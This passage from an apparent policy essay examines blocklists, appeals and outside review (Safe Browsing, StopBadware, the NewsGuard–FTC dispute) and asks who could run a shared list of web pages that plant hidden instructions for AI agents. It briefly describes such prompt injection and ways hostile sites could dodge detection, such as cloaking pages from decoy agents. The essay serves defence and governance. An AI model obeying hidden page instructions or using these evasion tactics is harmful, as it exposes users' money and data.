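| Safe Browsing and SmartScreen | Google or Microsoft | Broad categories of threat | The same company | The company's other products | Governments and the company's own interests |
| PhishTank | Volunteers who vote | Each report and its outcome | Volunteers and staff | Cisco | Groups of voters acting together |
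| APWG and Global Signal Exchange | Each member, for its own products | Little | Whichever member blocked the site | Members and sponsors | The largest contributors |
| Polish warning list | CERT Polska | The legal criteria and the whole list | The telecoms regulator | Taxpayers | The government of the day |

Only the Polish arrangement sends appeals to a body that didn't make the original decision. Regular outside audits with published error rates would also help, but the closest most lists seem to have is an occasional academic study.

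How owners and senders learn that they have been listed also varies. A blocked email sender usually finds out from a bounce message. Google notifies website owners, sometimes by emailing the address they registered with Search Console, its service for site owners. If a site repeatedly switches between compliant and noncompliant behaviour, Google bars its owner from requesting reviews through Search Console for 30 days. This makes it harder for attackers to clean a site just long enough to pass a review. But an honest site that Google wrongly flags, clears and flags again, as happened to Immich, could look much like a repeat offender.

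### StopBadware and outside review

Techdirt's *Stopping Malware In Search Leads To Unsupported Claims Of Bias* describes how Google once enlisted StopBadware, a nonprofit project that began at Harvard in 2006, to help review complaints from sites on its malware list. Infopackets' *Google Accused of Wrongly Identifying Websites as Dangerous* reports that StopBadware promised to answer within ten business days.

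StopBadware also made the process easier to follow. Leahy's *Announcing Review Request History* describes a public page for each reported site that showed when the site entered the database and when its owner appealed. A shop owner could use the page to prove to customers that an appeal was under way, and researchers could use it to measure delays.

But StopBadware had no power to remove a warning. According to StopBadware's own website, Google decided independently whether to warn visitors, and StopBadware posted the addresses Google sent it without checking them first. Google was also one of its funders. It is unclear how often StopBadware's reviews changed Google's decisions.

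StopBadware became an independent organisation in 2010 and a university research project in 2015, then closed in 2020. A similar reviewer for agents would need steadier funding, perhaps from a fixed fee paid by every company that uses the list, and companies would have to agree in advance to follow its decisions.

### How much a list can publish

A site owner needs to know why their site is on a list, but an attacker can use the same explanation to avoid detection. *My experience being blocked by Google Safe Browsing* (2022) is by a site owner who had worked against spam and fraud and understood that secrecy makes a detection system harder to beat. But when Google called the owner's site deceptive, the owner had to guess what was wrong, and the browser, Google's public status page and the review request often gave conflicting information.

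According to Lewis and Sergeant, an operator that publishes its criteria need not disclose the exact algorithms or data behind an entry. It should keep a record of the evidence for each entry, but any public version can omit details that would help spammers, such as the location of a spamtrap. They warn that abusers may exploit rules that are too explicit, for example about when entries expire.

Secrecy is also less reliable than operators might hope. Li and colleagues found 140,449 domains that led to Spamhaus's secret spamtraps, and patient attackers could probably do the same.

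The operator of a list of pages with hidden instructions could be fairly open about why a page is listed, because the evidence is on the page. If the operator quoted the hidden text to a camera shop, the owner could find and delete the review that contained it. An attacker would learn that the operator had noticed that wording, but could also learn that by checking whether the page was listed.

The exact time of the visit is more sensitive. If the operator uses decoy agents, a dishonest owner could look up that time in the server's logs, find the decoy's IP address and show that address a clean page from then on. The operator could give only the date, or have several decoys visit before it sends the notice.

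### What sharing adds

*Helping Hands* (Bouwman et al., 2022) tested the value of sharing by studying the COVID-19 Cyber Threat Coalition, which more than 4,000 volunteers joined during the pandemic to pool reports of malicious sites. The group mostly collected what the security industry already knew. It checked reports against the security tools on VirusTotal and set a high threshold for listing, which kept false positives low but rejected many of the volunteers' own discoveries. As a result, at most 3.6% of the domains on its blocklist were related to COVID-19.

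The volunteers did add new information about the small group of COVID-related domains. When the coalition listed these domains, existing abuse-detection systems had already detected about 25% of them, compared with 58% of all the domains on its list.

Sharing therefore seems most useful for threats that existing tools aren't designed to detect, such as many pages written to mislead agents. But a shared list could easily repeat the coalition's mistake. If it included only pages that several malware scanners had flagged, it would leave out a fake camera review with a hidden instruction, because the page contains no malware. Its operator would need a different test, such as opening the page with a decoy agent and checking for the reported text.

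### NewsGuard and the Federal Trade Commission

Operators can usually settle a dispute about malware by testing the site again. Disputes about whether a publisher is truthful are much harder to settle, as a long-running one in the United States shows.

NewsGuard, a company founded in 2018 by the journalists Steven Brill and Gordon Crovitz, rates news sources from 0 to 100. According to NewsGuard's *Complaint for Declaratory and Injunctive Relief* (2026), its staff award points for nine published criteria, such as whether a site repeatedly publishes false claims, corrects its errors and discloses its owners. They invite a site to respond before they publish its score, and they print relevant comments alongside the score. The company says that more than 2,000 sites have improved their practices as a result. Through these steps, NewsGuard gives the sources it rates more notice and explanation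 than most security lists do.

Advertisers use the ratings to avoid placing ads on unreliable sites, and NewsGuard also licenses them to AI companies. NewsGuard's *Microsoft's Copilot* (2024) said that the ratings could inform Copilot's answers. Microsoft may since have ended this arrangement. *Microsoft Told Ted Cruz It Had Nothing To Do With NewsGuard*, from the conservative news site The Daily Wire, reports that Microsoft distanced itself from NewsGuard and removed some references to it.

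Critics consider NewsGuard's ratings biased against conservatives. Sibarium (2026), in *A Media Watchdog Is Helping To Program AI Models*, objects that NewsGuard rates Chinese propaganda as more reliable than many American news sources. A points system can produce surprising rankings because a site earns points for disclosing its owner as well as for accuracy. NewsGuard replies that its criteria are not political and that Fox News scores higher than the left-leaning MSNBC. It also says two advocacy groups accused it of opposite biases within a few months. Both groups could be partly right, so their conflicting accusations don't prove the scores are fair.

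In May 2025, the US Federal Trade Commission (FTC), which enforces competition law, demanded extensive records from NewsGuard for an investigation into advertising boycotts, and the dispute then grew.

1. In September 2025, the FTC approved the merger of two advertising companies, Omnicom and Interpublic, on conditions that U.S. Press Freedom Tracker's *FTC demands records from NewsGuard about its media ratings* describes as effectively barring Omnicom from using NewsGuard.
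2. In February 2026, NewsGuard sued the FTC. It asked the court to block both the demand for records and the merger condition.
3. In April, three more agencies, WPP, Publicis and Dentsu, settled FTC charges on similar terms. The FTC then dropped its demand, saying that the settlements had made the records unnecessary.
4. The trial judge refused NewsGuard an early injunction because it had not shown irreparable harm. She left it free to ask again, but NewsGuard appealed.
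5. On 6 October 2026, appeal judges questioned NewsGuard's lawyer about what harm the FTC had caused, as Law360's *DC Circ. Probes NewsGuard Over Harm From FTC Orders* reports. The appeal seems to be still undecided.

Havas accepted a similar order by the time of that hearing or soon after. The FTC says it was the last of the six biggest advertising agencies to do so.

According to PYMNTS's *Ad Agencies Resolve FTC Charges of Illegal Digital Ad Boycotts*, the FTC alleged that the agencies had colluded through trade associations since 2018 to impose common "brand safety" standards, instead of competing over how to place advertisements. In *Order Denying Petition to Quash Civil Investigative Demand*, FTC chairman Ferguson denies singling out NewsGuard, since 17 recipients, including NewsGuard, were sent civil investigative demands. He also argues that the investigation can't have silenced NewsGuard,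 because it didn't change what it published in the nine months after receiving the demand.

NewsGuard argues that the investigation punishes it for opinions the government dislikes. It points to Ferguson's earlier public attacks on the company and to the breadth of the demand, which covered its work since 2018. It told the FTC that its legal costs had exceeded 28% of its revenue from the advertising services under investigation. It also argues that the First Amendment bars the government from correcting perceived bias in private speech, even if NewsGuard's ratings are biased.

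Both sides could be partly right. Competitors may break the law by agreeing to use the same list, however accurate it is, and a government may violate free speech by restricting a list, even if some of the list's users colluded. The courts have not decided either point in this dispute. The advertising companies settled without a trial, and WPP neither admitted nor denied the allegations. A New York court did dismiss a defamation suit against NewsGuard in 2025, ruling that its ratings of the left-leaning Consortium News were protected opinion.

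A related case is somewhat encouraging for NewsGuard. In *Media Matters for America v. Federal Trade Commission* (2025), the same appeals court, the D.C. Circuit, left in place an order blocking the FTC's demand to Media Matters, another critic of conservative media. But it was an early ruling about a different organisation, and one judge dissented.

The FTC's settlement with WPP bars the company from using lists based on "viewpoints as to the veracity of news reporting" or on outside journalistic standards, but exempts fraudulent content (U.S. District Court for the Northern District of Texas, *Final Order and Stipulated Permanent Injunction as to GroupM Worldwide LLC*, 2026). An advertiser can still tell WPP to use such a list for its own campaigns, but WPP can't offer that list to another client.

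The order covers advertising in the United States and doesn't apply to AI agents. But if several AI companies adopted one list of untruthful publishers, they could face the same accusation of collusion. A shared list of phishing sites would be easier to defend. A list of pages with hidden instructions would fall in between. Anyone can verify that the hidden text is there, but the web surveys showed that people disagree about which instructions are malicious.

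### What exists for agents

Agent companies, including Microsoft and Anthropic, have mainly built private lists and checks. Some data is public. Unit 42 publishes addresses from its own investigations, and the small MoltThreats feed accepts reports from agents. Both have far less reach than Spamhaus or Safe Browsing.

NewsGuard now offers two products that apply its ratings to AI answers. In May 2026, NewsGuard (2026) updated its browser extension to show scores next to the sources that ChatGPT and Gemini cite. This leaves the choice of ratings to the user, but the scores appear only after the assistant has read the sources, so they can't keep hostile text away from it. In June, NewsGuard (2026) launched a chatbot that answers only from about 12,000 publishers the company has approved. NewsGuard both writes this allowlist and sells the product that depends on it.

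Two other efforts to share information could eventually carry reports of hostile pages, though both have much wider aims. In 2025, members of the Frontier Model Forum, an industry group that includes Anthropic, Google, Microsoft and OpenAI, agreed to exchange information about threats and vulnerabilities. The US government's AI Action Plan of July 2025 proposed a national centre for sharing information about AI security threats.

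Engineers at the IETF are working on a way for agents to sign their requests so that websites can recognise them. This would help sites tell real agents from impostors, but it would also make cloaking easier, because a hostile site could show its hidden instructions only to visitors with a valid signature. Decoy agents would then need signatures that sites can't distinguish from those of ordinary agents.

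A shared list would need little new technology. An operator could use the IETF's 2013 reputation format and add a claim such as "contains hidden instructions to AI systems". Agreeing on which instructions count would be harder.

### Who could run a list for agents

AI companies could continue to run their own lists. Each company could block an attack within minutes of detecting it, without waiting for a committee. Users would also know whom to blame for a mistake. But a company may have to judge its competitors, and outsiders can't easily check whether it does so fairly. Each company would also learn mainly from attacks on its own users.

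A joint body would let companies share what they learn about hostile pages. Suppose, for illustration, that it takes 100 agent visits to detect a hostile page. If five companies work separately, the page can reach 500 agents before all of them block it. If they share reports, it reaches about 100. If the five companies' agents visit equally often, sharing also gives the attacker a fifth as long to earn back the price of the domain.

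Sharing would benefit the largest company least. If one company ran 60% of the agents, sharing would reduce the number of its agents that reached the page from 100 to 60. For a company with 5%, the number would fall from 100 to 5. The largest company would also supply most of the evidence, so it might prefer to keep its data private or sell it.

A joint list would also spread mistakes and poisoned reports to every member's agents. The joint body could reduce this risk by sharing evidence instead of verdicts, as the phishing exchanges do, and letting each company decide what to block. This would probably also make accusations of collusion easier to answer. But small companies without their own reviewers would be tempted to block everything in the feed, which would leave their blocking decisions to the joint body.

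A public authority could offer criteria set by law, a right to reasons and an independent appeal, which private operators rarely provide. It would also have no camera shop or search engine of its own to favour. However, a government that controlled the list could influence what millions of agents read. Many people would object even if the list began with only phishing sites, because a later government could add publishers it disliked. The NewsGuard dispute shows how quickly judgements about sources can become political. A national authority would also struggle to review sites in languages its staff don't read.

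It might be safer to let a public body hear appeals without letting it add entries. The body could then correct a private company's mistakes but couldn't block a newspaper. It would need enough staff to answer within days, and companies would need a fast way to relist a site that resumed attacking agents.

Users could also choose their own lists. This would suit ratings of truthfulness, because people who distrust NewsGuard could pick another service or none, and no company would have to impose one view of the news on everyone. But most people would probably keep the default, as the owners of nearly 186,000 domains did when they left the choice of spam list to Outlook. Few users could judge which list best catches hidden instructions, and a bad choice could expose an employer's passwords as well as the user's own data.

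For that reason, AI companies should probably turn on protection against hidden instructions by default and pool the evidence it relies on, but leave ratings of truthfulness to the user. The two should also stay on separate lists, so that users can reject someone's opinion of a newspaper without losing protection against a page that tells the agent to send money.
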